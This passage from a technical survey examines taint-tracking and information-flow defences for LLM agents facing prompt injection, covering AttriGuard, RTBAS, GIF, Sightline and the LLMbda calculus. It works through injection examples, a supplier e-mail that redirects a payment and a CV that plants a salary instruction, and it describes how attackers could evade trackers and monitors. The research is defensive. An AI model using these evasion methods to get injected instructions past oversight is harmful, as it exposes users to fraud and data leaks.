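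MemLineage also treats a memory as trusted if the agent didn't record where it came from. A stricter setting blocks sensitive actions based on such memories, but it also blocks actions based on a reminder that the user saved directly. The ordinary join rule would keep the label through any number of summaries, but it would also cause more label creep.

### Testing a call before making it

NeuroTaint detects flows but doesn't prevent them. In the invoice example, it could report that the supplier's e-mail had determined the account number, but only after the money had been sent. It can still help investigate incidents. NeuroTaint flagged 203 of the 400 scenarios, of which 187 were real flows and 16 were false alarms. Claude Opus 4.6 then reviewed the flagged scenarios, judging 179 of the real flows unsafe and dismissing all 16 false alarms.

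A counterfactual test can prevent harm if it runs before the tool call. *AttriGuard*, by He, Zhu and colleagues (2026), reruns the agent's model on the same history, with the tool results rewritten to weaken any instructions while keeping the facts. If the proposed call disappears or changes substantially, AttriGuard blocks it. This roughly doubles the number of tokens the agent uses. None of the attacks that weren't adapted to AttriGuard succeeded. Attacks optimised against it succeeded 6.6% of the time on Gemini 2.5, compared with 29.5% to 82.0% for the other defences tested this way.

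Other systems use variants of the test. *CausalArmor* (2026) removes one piece of the input at a time and measures the effect on the model's output. *AgentSentry* (2026) compares four reruns, with the user's request either intact or masked and the tool results either original or cleaned.

A basic difficulty is that harmless tool results are supposed to influence what the agent does. *Influence Is Not Authority* (Ahad, Hossain et al., 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to send money to Alice. The user can supply Alice's account number, or the agent can look it up with a banking tool. Either way, the user has authorised the same payment. Ahad and colleagues built 24 cases like this and scored them with their own reconstruction of CausalArmor's measure, because its code wasn't available. In all 24, the action looked more like an attack when the value came from a tool. On average,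 getting the value from a tool changed the score more than replacing Alice with a recipient the user hadn't authorised.

They also tested AttriGuard on these cases. It blocked 47.1% of the authorised actions and 36.3% of the unauthorised ones, a difference that could be due to chance. AttriGuard did much better in He and colleagues' tests. Ahad and colleagues designed their cases to separate influence from permission, so the figures don't show how AttriGuard would do on ordinary tasks, although looking up a missing account number is an ordinary thing for an agent to do.

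The two registered accounts are difficult for a different reason. He and colleagues discuss a user who asks the agent to e-mail Alice if a web page is in English and Bob otherwise. They accept that the page's language may determine which of them gets the e-mail, and see an attack only if the page makes the agent do something else, such as e-mail Carol. Likewise, if the user has told the agent to use whichever account the e-mail indicates, an attacker who picks the second account is making a choice the user allowed.

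### If human review depends on taint

A system can also ask a person to approve sensitive calls whenever the session is tainted. Aljumaily and colleagues simulated what happens when the tracker sometimes loses the taint label. In their simulation, a fully compromised model tries every available attack on 13 tasks. An automatic monitor blocks calls that break its policy, and a human reviews some of the rest.

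The simulation rates the severity of each action from 0 to 10. Writing a file is a 3, for example, and changing a configuration is a 9. In a tainted session, the reviewer sees every call rated 3 or higher. Calls above a second, higher threshold go to the reviewer whether or not the session is tainted. The reviewer catches a bad call with probability

$$h=0.9\times\max(0.3,\;1-0.3L)\times 0.93^{k},$$

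where $L$ is the average number of legitimate requests per task, which tire the reviewer, and $k$ counts earlier attempts and requests. Aljumaily and colleagues chose all these numbers themselves and didn't test the review process with real people or models.

The table shows the results as the tracker labelled fewer of the attacked sessions. Harm is the severity of the worst unauthorised action in each episode, averaged over all episodes. A severe action is one rated 8 or higher. The strong monitor allows only what the task requires, while the weaker one checks the arguments of each call.

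| Attacked sessions labelled | Strong monitor, always review 10: harm | Weaker monitor, always review 10: severe actions | Weaker monitor, always review 8 or higher: severe actions |
|---|---|---|---|
| 100% | 0.21 | 1.5% | 1.7% |
| 80% | 0.32 | 2.8% | 1.7% |
| 40% | 0.50 | 5.1% | 1.7% |
| 0% | 0.69 | 7.7% | 1.7% |

With the strong monitor, no severe action got through even when the tracker lost every label. Harm rose only to 0.69, the level the monitor allows without human review.

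With the weaker monitor, the effect of losing taint labels depended on the second threshold. Raising that threshold from 8 to 10 saves the reviewer time, but actions rated 8 or 9 then reach a person only if the session has a taint label. With the threshold at 10, the rate of severe actions rose fivefold when the tracker lost every label. At 8, the rate didn't change, because a person reviewed those actions with or without a label.

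The simulation labels whole sessions and loses labels at random. Real trackers tend to miss the same kinds of flow every time, so an attacker who knows the tracker can use a kind it misses. Against that attacker, a tracker that finds 93.5% of flows on a benchmark may offer no more protection than that shown in the bottom row of the table.

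## Sightline and its predecessors: which inputs should label a model's output

Giving a model's reply the context label, as FIDES does, misses no flow within one conversation, but it soon labels almost everything.

For an ordinary library function, a tracker can do better by using a *data-flow summary*, which lists the arguments that reach the result. A programmer or an analysis tool derives the summary from the function's code. A model call has no code that shows which inputs reach the output. The model may copy an input, reduce it to a yes or no, or ignore it, depending on the prompt.

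In ordinary programs, joining the labels of all the inputs to a model call is usually right. *Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) studied model calls from 2,103 families of open-source repositories, each a repository and its forks. These programs fill the *placeholders* in a prompt template with values such as a user's question or a retrieved document. The model's output made no visible use of 12–14% of the placeholders. Including their labels is a small error for one call, but in an agent each unneeded label spreads to every later step.

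### Dropping inputs and generating again

A model's output can carry a less restrictive label if the model sees fewer inputs. Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, keep only the labels of inputs that influenced the output. As Costa and colleagues describe the method, it finds a subset of the messages that accounts for the response, then has the model regenerate the response from that subset alone. The new response needs only the labels of the messages in the subset.

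Generating the reply again without the e-mail makes this reasonably safe, because the e-mail can't steer a reply when it isn't in the prompt. If the user typed an account number that an e-mail happens to repeat, the model can write the same payment without the e-mail, so the payment can keep its trusted label.

Siddiqui and colleagues built one version of their method for prompts with retrieved documents and another for a language model that looks up similar stored text as it predicts each token. In more than 85% of cases tested with an agent, their method beat a baseline that asks the model to predict the label of its own output.

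Finding the subset takes the most computation, since $n$ inputs have $2^n$ subsets. *RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025) estimates that even the optimised search needs 16 to 64 extra model calls per response with four to six security levels.

RTBAS (Robust Tool-Based Agent System) replaces the search with a *screener* that predicts which parts of the conversation matter for the agent's next step. RTBAS joins the labels of those parts and blanks out every part of the conversation whose label is more restrictive than this join. The model then writes the next step from what is left. If the tool's policy forbids the resulting label, RTBAS asks the user.

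One of its two screeners is a second language model that lists the relevant parts. The other uses *attention*, the weights inside a model that determine how much it draws on each earlier token. A small open model computes the attention, and a neural network trained on 40 AgentDojo test cases uses it to classify each part as relevant or not. This network was 81% accurate on test data.

Zhong and colleagues argue that these screening mistakes can't compromise security, because the model never sees what the screener wrongly left out. This is nearly true, but the screener does read the attacker's e-mail, so the e-mail can influence which label it chooses. RTBAS then shows the model everything that label permits, so the attacker controls only the label. If the label is "trusted", the model bases its decision on trusted text alone, and if it is "untrusted", the payment tool requires the user's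 confirmation. The attacker can therefore influence whether a payment goes through automatically but not where it goes. This resembles the one bit per run that the no-sensitive-upgrade rule leaks.

RTBAS's other assumptions could do more harm. It treats text without a label as public and trusted, the unsafe default that positive tainting reverses. It also relies on tools to preserve labels. In an example from Zhong and colleagues, an agent is allowed to put private data in a message to the user, and a second tool returns sent messages labeled as public. The agent could remove a secret's private label by sending it to the user and reading the message back.

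On AgentDojo, RTBAS prevented every targeted attack, and the agent's task performance fell by only about 2%. But the attention screener was trained on the same benchmark, so it may do worse elsewhere.

### What survives a model call

It would help to know what models typically do with their inputs. Xu, Meng and colleagues (2026), in *Crossing the NL/PL Divide*, collected 9,083 pairs of a placeholder and a model's output from 4,154 Python files. (NL/PL stands for natural language and programming language.) The first version of the paper, from March 2026, sorts the pairs into 24 categories, most of which belong to one of five levels:

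| What survives | Input | Output |
|---|---|---|
| The wording | "GDP of France" | a sentence containing "GDP of France" |
| The meaning | "fix the login bug" | "Resolve the authentication issue" |
| The main points | a 500-word document | a two-sentence summary |
| A signal | a product review | a score of 4 |
| Nothing | "You are a helpful assistant" | no trace of the text |

A tracker can drop a security label only at the bottom level, which covers inputs that the model ignored, refused to act on, or couldn't use because it lacked information or tools. A yes-or-no answer keeps its label.

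Xu, Meng and colleagues used the categories to predict whether a placeholder's content could reach a dangerous operation, such as running code or a database command. They first discarded the placeholders at the bottom level, then had a language model trace the output through the rest of the program. On 353 pairs labelled by experts, the paper's first version reports an F1 of 92.3%. A revised version, with 25 categories and a smaller dataset, reports 81.7%, against 47.5% for assuming that everything flows. Most of that improvement probably comes from tracing the program, because the category "ignored" applied to only 26 of the 243 pairs without a flow. Across the revised dataset, just 7% of placeholders were entirely at the bottom level.

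These categories describe what the model did with one particular value, but an attacker may be able to choose another. Reviewers judged that in four of the 30 pairs marked "ignored", an attacker who controlled the placeholder could still reach the dangerous operation. (A pair can have several categories.) Likewise, a model that refuses one request may comply with a rewording of it.

Labelling each call this way is also slow. Xu, Li and colleagues used the same kind of procedure to create their reference data, and it took about 10,400 tokens and 13 seconds per placeholder for each labelling model.

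### Measuring sensitivity with GIF

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests replacing yes-or-no labels with measures of how much information an output carries about each labelled input. In *GIF* (Geometric Information Flow), Štorek, Holzer and colleagues (2026) compute such a measure from the model's internals.

A model first converts each token into a list of numbers called an *embedding*. GIF measures how much the next token $Y$ would reveal about a little random noise $U$ if that noise were added to the embeddings of one stretch of the prompt, such as a sentence in an e-mail. This quantity, the *mutual information* $I(U;Y)$, is zero if the next token is independent of the noise.

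Calculating this exactly would take too long for a large model, so GIF uses an upper bound based on three matrices. The *Jacobian* $J$ gives the change in the model's last internal state for a small change in the embeddings. $W$ converts that state into *logits*, one score for every possible next token. The third matrix, $F=\mathrm{diag}(p)-pp^\top$, accounts for the step from logits to the probabilities $p$. Together they give

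$$M=J^\top W^\top F\,W J,$$

and for noise with variance $\tau$,

$$I(U;Y)\;\le\;\tfrac12\log\det(\mathrm{Id}+\tau M)+o(\tau),$$

where $\mathrm{Id}$ is the identity matrix. The bound is large if noise in many directions would noticeably shift the probabilities. The error term $o(\tau)$ shrinks faster than $\tau$ does as the noise gets weaker.

Štorek and colleagues call this property "locally sound" and provide a machine-checked proof. The proof covers the effect of one stretch of one prompt on one next token, for very weak noise, if the model behaves smoothly near that prompt. It doesn't cover replacing the e-mail with a different one, which is the change an attacker makes and the kind noninterference concerns.

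Computing $J$ alone would take thousands of passes through a large model, so GIF uses a few random probes to estimate the sum of $M$'s diagonal entries, which is enough to rank the inputs.

In one example, an agent screens job applicants, and a CV contains an instruction to recommend the candidate at a salary of $200,000, which the agent obeys. GIF assigns 82 bits to the injected instruction, 27 to the employer's criteria and 16 to the rest. These figures measure how sensitive the recommendation is to each part, not how many bits of the CV it reveals.

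In a broader test, Štorek and colleagues checked whether GIF's top-ranked tokens came from the injection more often when an attack had succeeded. They report the AUROC, which here is the chance that a random successful attack scores higher than a random other run, so 0.5 is no better than guessing. On AgentDojo, GIF averaged 0.75 with the top five tokens and 0.91 with the top 50, against 0.56 and 0.84 for their reimplementation of RTBAS's attention method. RTBAS did better on one of the six models, Gemma 4.

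GIF can also find flows that AgentDojo's scoring misses. In one run, an agent sent an e-mail to the attacker's address but with the wrong contents, so the benchmark counted the attack as a failure. GIF attributed 31% of the information in the address to the injection.

A high score doesn't show whether the user wanted the flow, so Štorek and colleagues pass the top-ranked passages to a language model, which allows or denies the action. On two benchmarks, the small Qwen 3 8B given these passages matched GPT-5.5 given the full record, at less than an eightieth of the cost.

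### Why a confident answer can hide its source

Low scores are harder to interpret. In another example, an agent turns private notes into a public comment and leaves out a home address. GIF gives the address a flow of zero, and Štorek and colleagues say GIF can "certify zero flow". But a score near zero can also mean that an input settled the answer so firmly that small changes to the input no longer affect it.

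The reason is the way models turn logits into probabilities. If the chosen token $y$ has logit $z_y$ and probability $p_y$, then

$$\log p_y=z_y-\log\sum_c e^{z_c},\qquad \frac{\partial \log p_y}{\partial z_y}=1-p_y.$$

At a probability of 0.5, this derivative is 0.5. At 0.999, it is 0.001.

Suppose the invoice assistant's model must answer "first" or "second" to choose one of the supplier's accounts. Let $u=1$ if the e-mail says "we have changed banks" and $u=-1$ if it doesn't. The logit for "second" is $6.9u$ and the logit for "first" is always 0. The probability of "second" is then 0.999 with the announcement and 0.001 without it, so the e-mail decides almost everything. But with the announcement present, the gradient with respect to $u$ is only

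$$6.9\times(1-0.999)\approx 0.007.$$

For an undecided model, at $u=0$, it would be about 3.45, or 500 times larger.

The matrix $F$ in GIF has the same weakness. With two possible tokens, every entry has magnitude $p(1-p)$, which is 0.25 for an undecided model but about 0.001 here. GIF's theorem still holds, because weak noise has almost no effect on the answer, but removing the e-mail's label because of its low score would be a mistake. Such confident outputs are common. Xu, Li and colleagues found that Qwen3-8B assigned less than 1% of the probability to other tokens in one of every five outputs.

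Deleting the whole e-mail would reveal its influence in this example, because the answer would change. However, deletion tests fail when the prompt contains the same information twice. Say the attacker's account number appears both in the e-mail and in an attached invoice. Let $f(a,b)$ be 1 if the model pays that account and 0 otherwise, where $a$ and $b$ record whether each copy is present. One copy is enough, so

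$$f(1,1)-f(0,1)=0,\qquad f(1,1)-f(1,0)=0,\qquad f(1,1)-f(0,0)=1.$$

An attacker can defeat a tracker that tests inputs one at a time by pasting the same number twice. Deleting either copy alone doesn't change the model's output, so the tracker would drop both labels and treat the attacker's number as trusted. NeuroTaint's counterfactual test has the same problem.

Generating the response again avoids the error. If the tracker removes only the e-mail, the new payment depends on the invoice and gets the invoice's label. If it removes both the e-mail and the invoice, the model has no number to pay.

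### Reading attention with Sightline

Sightline, published in November 2026, looks for evidence that doesn't weaken as the model gets more confident. It uses attention, as RTBAS does, but treats each *attention head* separately. Heads are small units in a model that fetch information from earlier tokens. In a standard transformer, the design behind most language models, they are the only parts that move information between token positions.

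At position $t$, a head computes a weighted average of information from earlier positions, with weight $a_{ts}$ for position $s$. Xu, Li and colleagues show that the effect of a small change at $s$ on the head's output at $t$ is at most

$$a_{ts}\times c_{ts},$$

where $c_{ts}$ depends on the head and its current inputs. If the weight is zero, a small change at $s$ has no effect at $t$ through that head. By chaining this result through the layers, they prove that an input can have a first-order effect on the output only if a route of non-zero attention weights connects them. Like GIF's result, this proof is machine-checked and concerns small changes.

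The theorem rarely clears an input on its own, because ordinary attention gives every visible token at least a little weight. Could a tracker ignore inputs with a tiny weight? Xu, Li and colleagues prove that this isn't safe either. In their counterexample, which I'll call the quiet head, the weight on an input is

$$a=\frac{1}{1+e^{-20u}}.$$

Suppose the input is the supplier's e-mail, with $u$ defined as before. If the e-mail doesn't announce a change of banks, its weight is about two billionths. If it does, the weight is almost 1 and the answer flips. The e-mail decides the answer in both cases, but its influence is visible only in the second. Xu, Li and colleagues compare this to an implicit flow through a branch not taken, as in Fenton's program.

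A large weight doesn't prove that the model used the input, either. The head may discard what it reads, or another head may cancel its contribution.

Sightline therefore learns from examples which patterns of attention indicate real use. It runs the model once over the recorded prompt and output. For each attention head, it records the average and highest attention from the output to a placeholder, and the placeholder's share of all attention to the prompt. Qwen3-8B has 1,152 heads, so this gives 3,456 numbers. A logistic regression combines them into a score, and Sightline drops the label if the score is below a threshold.

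Some of the regression's weights are negative, so extra attention from certain heads lowers the score. Forcing every weight to be positive made Sightline less accurate. But with negative weights, the theorem about attention routes no longer justifies dropping a label, so any guarantee must be statistical.

### How many labels Sightline removes

Xu, Li and colleagues trained Sightline on an older set of 8,105 pairs and tested it on 4,918 new ones for each of four small open models. The real programs' data wasn't available, so a language model generated plausible values for the placeholders. Three other models (GPT-6 Astra, Claude Opus 5.5 and DeepSeek-V4.1) judged whether each output visibly used each value. A "true flow" in these results is therefore one that models like these can detect, which may exclude an e-mail that affected the output only because it lacked a sentence.

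In a separate test that didn't rely on judges, the prompts contained planted unique names, numbers and web addresses. Sightline found all 476 flows in which the output repeated a planted value.

The next table compares Sightline with three other methods. The first column of results shows the share of unneeded labels that each method removed when calibrated to miss about 1% of true flows. The other columns show the AUROC for telling true flows from non-flows on two difficult kinds of input. Each range covers the four models.

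| Method | Unneeded labels removed | AUROC, information repeated twice more | AUROC, most confident fifth of outputs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sightline | 43.9–65.6% | 0.99–1.00 | 0.91–0.96 |
| RTBAS's attention method | 14.7–29.4% | 0.84–0.99 | 0.83–0.89 |
| Deleting one input | 13.2–18.9% | 0.54–0.69 | 0.84–0.89 |
| GIF, over 32 tokens | 0.6–12.1% | 0.63–0.74 | 0.63–0.75 |

GIF removes so few labels because many true flows in confident outputs score close to zero. To miss only 1% of flows, its threshold must be even lower, and hardly any unneeded labels score below it. Xu, Li and colleagues implemented the other methods themselves, and Štorek and colleagues designed GIF to find the source of an attack, not to clear harmless inputs. Still, the results fit the mathematics of confident answers and repeated inputs.

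Sightline removes 43.9–65.6% of the unneeded labels, but only 12–14% of all labels were unneeded, so it removes about 5–9% of all labels this way. It also misses 1% of the true flows, which means it wrongly removes a little under 1% of all labels. Very roughly, one in ten of the labels that Sightline removes should have stayed.

Sightline at least takes little time to run. Reading a recorded call took 0.12–0.20 seconds, and recording the attention while Qwen3-8B generated its output added about 2% to the generation time. Sightline also works with closed models, whose attention outsiders can't see, by running their prompts and outputs through an open model and using that model's attention instead. In tests that treated the four open models as closed, this changed accuracy by between −4.2 and +3.2 points.

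### How conformal prediction limits missed flows

The 1% limit comes from *conformal prediction*, a statistical method that works with any scoring system. Xu, Li and colleagues start with repository families whose true flows they know and pick one flow at random from each. They pick only one because flows in the same program tend to be missed together.

With $n$ families and an allowed miss rate of $\alpha$, they sort the $n$ scores and use the $k$-th lowest as the threshold, where

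$$k=\lfloor\alpha(n+1)\rfloor.$$

For example, with 999 families and a 1% limit, $k$ is 10. If a true flow comes from a new family that nothing distinguishes from the old ones, its score is equally likely to take any of the 1,000 places in the combined ranking. The chance that the score falls below the threshold, causing Sightline to miss the flow, is therefore at most 10 in 1,000.

*Exchangeability* is the assumption that nothing distinguishes the new case from the old ones. Formally, shuffling the old and new cases doesn't change their joint probability distribution. The assumption held up reasonably well across different collections of repositories. When calibrated on the older collection, Sightline still missed about 1% of flows on the new one and removed 43.8–60.1% of the unneeded labels.

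The limit on missed flows applies to the average, so Sightline can miss far more of some kinds of flow. In an analysis with Qwen3-8B and an overall limit of 5%, it missed 10.1% of flows in the most confident fifth of outputs, which could easily include a choice between two bank accounts. Setting a separate threshold for each fifth fixes this with little drawback, and Sightline then removes 42.5–61.0% of the unneeded labels with a 1% limit.

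### Label creep on AgentDojo

Xu, Li and colleagues also applied Sightline to an agent under attack. They took 120 recorded steps in which a Qwen3-8B agent called tools, drawn from 106 AgentDojo episodes, and used Sightline to decide which earlier inputs should label each call. Sightline removed 50.0% of the label creep, compared with 38.3% for the next best method, and had a miss rate of 3.9% per episode.

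This test allowed a miss rate of 5% instead of 1%, probably because there were too few episodes for the lower limit. Xu, Li and colleagues split the 106 episodes into five groups to keep calibration and testing separate, which left about 85 for calibration. With a 1% limit and fewer than 99 calibration cases, $k$ is 0 and Sightline can't remove any labels.

They then applied a policy like FIDES's, which blocks any consequential call with an untrusted label. None of the 34 attack calls got through, but with so few calls, the true rate of attacks getting through could still be as high as 8%. The test also barely separates good methods from bad ones. When only the injected tool outputs counted as untrusted, GIF and the deletion test let through at most one of the 34 attack calls on average, even though they were much worse at identifying which inputs mattered.

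The recorded steps don't show how many more tasks the agent would have completed. Removing half of the label creep could unblock far fewer than half of the wrongly blocked calls, because one remaining untrusted label is enough to block a call. If a harmless call has three irrelevant untrusted inputs, and Sightline has an independent 50% chance of removing the label from each, it removes all three labels only one time in eight.

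### When an attacker chooses the input

Exchangeability is a reasonable assumption for repositories written without Sightline in mind. It fails when an attacker who knows how Sightline works writes an e-mail to evade it, because that e-mail is not a random draw from the same population as the calibration data.

An attacker with no special knowledge can keep trying new wordings. If each one had an independent 1% chance of losing its label, at least one of 100 would lose it 63% of the time. A capable attacker could do better by testing wordings in private, looking for text that the agent obeys but whose attention pattern resembles that of an ignored input. If the agent runs on a closed model and Sightline reads it through an open one, the attacker can download the open model and search for wordings that mislead it. The AgentDojo test used the benchmark's existing attacks, so it doesn't show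 how hard it would be to find such wordings.

Rare attacks are a problem even if exchangeability holds. If one in 200 randomly drawn flows comes from an attack, Sightline could miss every attack flow and use only half of its 1% allowance. Calibrating on attacks alone would limit the average miss rate on attacks, but only for attacks like those in the sample.

The guarantee is more useful where nobody is trying to defeat it, for example when a company wants to estimate how often an agent accidentally includes private data in its replies.

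A safer approach against an attacker would be to use Sightline's answer to decide what to show the model, then generate the response again. This requires a second model call, but a wrongly dropped e-mail can't directly affect the new response. The agent should follow RTBAS's rule and keep every input that the chosen label permits. If it dropped each input that looked irrelevant, the attacker's e-mail could influence which of the supplier's two registered accounts stayed in the prompt, and the payment would still count as trusted.

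## The LLMbda calculus: a machine-checked guarantee for whole agents

Sightline's limit on missed flows is an average, and an attacker who chooses the input can get around it. Garby and colleagues wanted a guarantee that holds for every input, so they give each reply the label of the whole conversation, as FIDES does, rather than try to work out which inputs the model used. They prove that this is enough if the rest of the agent, including the loop that retries failed code, also follows the label rules.

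The *LLMbda calculus* (rhymes with "lambda") is a small programming language, designed for the proof, in which a developer can write a whole agent. CaMeL's leaks came from an interpreter whose rules existed only as Python code, and from a retry loop outside that interpreter. In LLMbda, the agent, its retry loop and any code the model writes are all programs in the same language, so one theorem about the language covers them all.

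### Four operations on a conversation

The *lambda calculus* is a programming language built almost entirely from functions. For example, `λx. x + 1` is the function that adds 1 to its input. Researchers like it because proofs about a language with few rules are shorter. LLMbda adds ordinary data such as numbers, strings and records, and it attaches labels to values. Each label has an integrity part and a confidentiality part.

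It also adds a current conversation with a language model, which has one label for all its messages. A program can do four things with it:

| Operation | Effect |
|---|---|
| `send` | adds a message to the conversation |
| `recv` | gets the model's reply and adds that too |
| `fork` | runs some code on a copy of the conversation, then discards the copy |
| `clear` | empties the conversation |

These are enough to build the dual-LLM pattern. To ask a quarantined model about an e-mail, the program forks the conversation, clears the copy, sends it the question and the e-mail, and receives the answer. The copy and the answer become untrusted, but the main conversation keeps its trusted label because it never contained the e-mail.

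Clearing a conversation also resets its label to the current program-counter label. This is safe because the old messages are no longer part of the model's input.

### The rules for sending and receiving

When a program sends a message, the interpreter first checks that the program-counter label may flow to the conversation's label. It then appends the message and sets

$$\ell_{\text{conversation}} := \ell_{\text{conversation}}\sqcup\ell_{\text{message}}.$$

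A trusted conversation therefore becomes untrusted as soon as the program sends it the supplier's e-mail.

Leaving out the probabilities, the rule for receiving is

$$\frac{pc\sqsubseteq\ell\qquad r=\text{the model's reply to }c\qquad \ell\;\vdash\;\ell:(c+r),\;\mathrm{parse}(r)\;\Downarrow\;C',V}{pc\;\vdash\;\ell:c,\;\mathtt{recv}\;\Downarrow\;C',V}$$

The statement below the bar follows once everything above it holds. It means that running `recv` with program-counter label $pc$, in a conversation $c$ with label $\ell$, produces a new conversation $C'$ and a value $V$. The interpreter makes the same check on $pc$ as before, obtains a reply $r$ and appends it to the conversation. It then reads the reply as code and runs it with the program-counter label set to $\ell$.

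Even a plain answer counts as code, so a reply of "42" is a program that returns 42. Its result gets the label $\ell$, like the result of any other program that runs under $\ell$.

This matters most when the reply contains instructions. Suppose the model has read the supplier's e-mail and replies with code that pays an account. The account number is a constant in the code, so CaMeL would treat it as trusted. LLMbda runs the code with an untrusted program-counter label, so the number is untrusted and the payment tool rejects it.

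Confidentiality works the same way. In the attack on CaMeL's retry loop, the planner wrote the balance into a new program as a public constant. If an LLMbda agent sends the model an error message that depends on the balance, the conversation becomes secret, and so does every constant in the code that the model writes afterwards.

Tools check labels with `assert`, which stops the program if a value's label isn't acceptable. A test that returns true or false is trickier because whether a value counts as secret can depend on another secret, so LLMbda gives the result its own label.

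### A message that depends on a secret

Garby and colleagues illustrate the check on the program-counter label with a short program. Here it is in Python style, where `ask` sends a message and receives the reply:

```python
ask("Remember this value: x = false")
if secret:
    ask("Set x = true")
answer = ask("Give me the value of x")
```

A weaker monitor might skip the check and join the program-counter label into the conversation's label whenever the program sends something. The table compares the two monitors. If the secret is false, they behave identically.

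| Step | Secret false, either monitor | Secret true, weaker monitor | Secret true, LLMbda |
|---|---|---|---|
| "Remember this value" | conversation public | conversation public | conversation public |
| "Set x = true" | not sent; still public | sent; conversation becomes secret | run stops |
| "Give me the value of x" | "false", public | "true", secret | never reached |

With the weaker monitor, an observer who receives the answer "false" learns that the secret is false, even though the answer's public label means it should not depend on the secret. The conversation has the same role as the variable `y` in Fenton's program. LLMbda applies the no-sensitive-upgrade rule to the conversation and stops the run, because the conversation is still public when whether to add to it depends on a secret.

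A developer can repair the program by labelling the first message as secret. The conversation is then secret in both runs, the program can send the second message, and the answer always comes back secret.

Without that preparation, a program that has branched on a secret can't call the model from inside the branch. Under the first published rules, from February 2026, it can't call even a quarantined model there, because the forked copy is still public and clearing it requires the same check.

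### Noninterference with random replies

The first version also assumed that a model always gives the same reply to the same conversation. Real models' replies are usually partly random, so two runs with the same inputs can differ. The second version, from July 2026, therefore compares the probabilities of results.

In one of its examples, a program prompts a model twice, in separate forks, to flip a coin that lands on heads 30% of the time, and returns the number of heads. The result is 0 with probability 0.7 × 0.7 = 0.49, 1 with probability 2 × 0.3 × 0.7 = 0.42, and 2 with probability 0.3 × 0.3 = 0.09. If some runs crashed or looped forever, these probabilities would add up to less than 1. Probabilities that add up to at most 1 form a *subdistribution*.

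Let $\mu_0$ and $\mu_1$ be the subdistributions of what an observer can see when the same program runs with two different secrets. They are *compatible* if there is a third subdistribution $\omega$ such that, for every visible result $q$,

$$\mu_0(q)\le\omega(q),\qquad \mu_1(q)\le\omega(q),\qquad\text{and}\qquad \sum_q\omega(q)\le 1.$$

We can think of $\omega$ as an imaginary program that ignores the secret. Each real run behaves like this program, except that the real run sometimes fails to produce a result. The secret may influence only which runs fail.

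*Termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference* (TIPNI) requires this for all pairs of secrets. Write $e_0\sim_m e_1$ if two programs differ only in data that an observer with clearance $m$ may not see, and likewise for their starting conversations. Then

$$C_0\sim_m C_1\;\text{ and }\;e_0\sim_m e_1\;\Rightarrow\;\mu_0\text{ and }\mu_1\text{ are compatible.}$$

Garby and colleagues prove that this holds at every clearance for every LLMbda program that doesn't use endorsement. If the program always finishes, both subdistributions add to 1, so they must be equal, and the observer sees the same probabilities whatever the secret is. If the program uses no randomness, TIPNI reduces to ordinary termination-insensitive noninterference.

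To prove the theorem they have to produce a suitable $\omega$. They define a second way to run any program, which skips a computation as soon as its label exceeds the observer's clearance and inserts a dummy value. This skipping version never uses the secret, so it has the same $\omega$ for both secrets. It also produces each visible result at least as often as the real program does, because a computation that it skips can't crash or loop. So

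$$\mu_0\le\omega\ge\mu_1.$$

Smith and Alpízar had used a similar idea for a simpler language by cutting the secret parts out of the program text before running it. That doesn't work for an agent, because the model writes part of the program during the run.

### How much failures can reveal

Suppose an agent fails to produce a result 4% of the time with one secret and 6% of the time with another. Its results might look like this:

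| Result | First secret | Second secret | Larger of the two |
|---|---|---|---|
| "approved" | 50% | 44% | 50% |
| "refused" | 46% | 50% | 50% |
| no result | 4% | 6% | |

The entries in the last column add up to 100%, so they form a valid $\omega$ and the two cases are compatible. If the first secret gave 52% and 44% instead, the larger values would add up to 102%, and the program would violate TIPNI.

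The *statistical distance* between the visible results is half the sum of their differences, here (6% + 4%)/2 = 5%. This is the most that TIPNI allows. For any two numbers, $|a-b|=2\max(a,b)-a-b$. If $d_0$ and $d_1$ are the two failure rates, summing over all visible results gives

$$\tfrac12\sum_q|\mu_0(q)-\mu_1(q)|=\sum_q\max(\mu_0(q),\mu_1(q))-\frac{(1-d_0)+(1-d_1)}{2}\le\frac{d_0+d_1}{2},$$

because the sum of the larger values can't exceed 1. The visible results therefore differ by at most the average failure rate.

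An observer who also notices failures can do slightly better. If we count "no result" as a third result, the distance in the table rises to 6%. An observer guessing which of two equally likely secrets the agent held would then be right 53% of the time, compared with 50% by chance.

This is reassuring only if failures are rare. TIPNI permits the "Remember this value" program, which fails every time if the secret is true and never if it is false.

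TIPNI ignores failures, which is easier to justify for endless loops than for errors. It follows a general recipe from *Reconciling Shannon and Scott with a Lattice of Computable Information* (Hunt, Sands and Stucki, 2022), which describes a function that returns 1 for even numbers and loops forever on odd ones. This function reveals less than one that returns 1 for even numbers and 0 for odd ones, because an observer waiting on an odd number can never be sure that the answer isn't about to arrive. But LLMbda also counts errors and blocked runs as failures, and an observer usually sees those at once. In *Nonmalleable Progress Leakage*, Cecchetti objects that guarantees of this kind ignore what a program's progress reveals, even though a secure system should prevent attackers from controlling such leaks.

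### Endorsement that can't release secrets

Some tasks, such as paying the account number in a supplier's e-mail, are possible only with endorsement. LLMbda therefore has an `endorse` operation, which takes a value and a target label. Writing each label as a pair of integrity and confidentiality, the result gets

$$(\,i_{pc}\sqcup i_{\text{target}},\;\; s_{pc}\sqcup s_{\text{value}}\,).$$

The target affects only the integrity part of the label, and the confidentiality part still comes from the value. If a program endorses a secret password, the password becomes trusted but stays secret. If the rule replaced the whole label, programs could use endorsement to publish secrets.

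Garby and colleagues prove that their version can't do this. They show that TIPNI holds for every observer who may see data of any integrity and is restricted only by secrecy, however many endorsements the program contains and whatever the attacker writes in the untrusted data. They call this property *insulated TIPNI*. In the invoice example, endorsing the account number can still let the money go to the attacker, but it can't make the customer's balance public.

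The $i_{pc}$ in the formula limits which code can endorse. If a model reads an untrusted e-mail and then writes code that calls `endorse`, that code runs with an untrusted program-counter label, so the call has no effect.

The agent can defeat this protection by mistakenly endorsing the text of the e-mail before showing it to the planner. The conversation then stays trusted, and so does any code the planner writes because of the e-mail. Garby and colleagues suggest a stricter wrapper that marks every value it endorses and stops the program if it tries to endorse a marked value. The mark spreads like any other label, so the planner's new code would carry it.

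A second wrapper, similar to FIDES's exception for small values, endorses only values from a fixed list. With eight e-mail categories, the attacker can choose at most three bits each time. The wrapper has to endorse the value before checking the list, because checking first would mean branching on untrusted data, and an endorsement inside that branch would have no effect. If the value is not on the list, the wrapper returns the original with its untrusted label. The three-bit limit has no formal proof yet, and the wrapper doesn't help with account numbers, which don't come from a short fixed list.

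### What the Lean proofs cover

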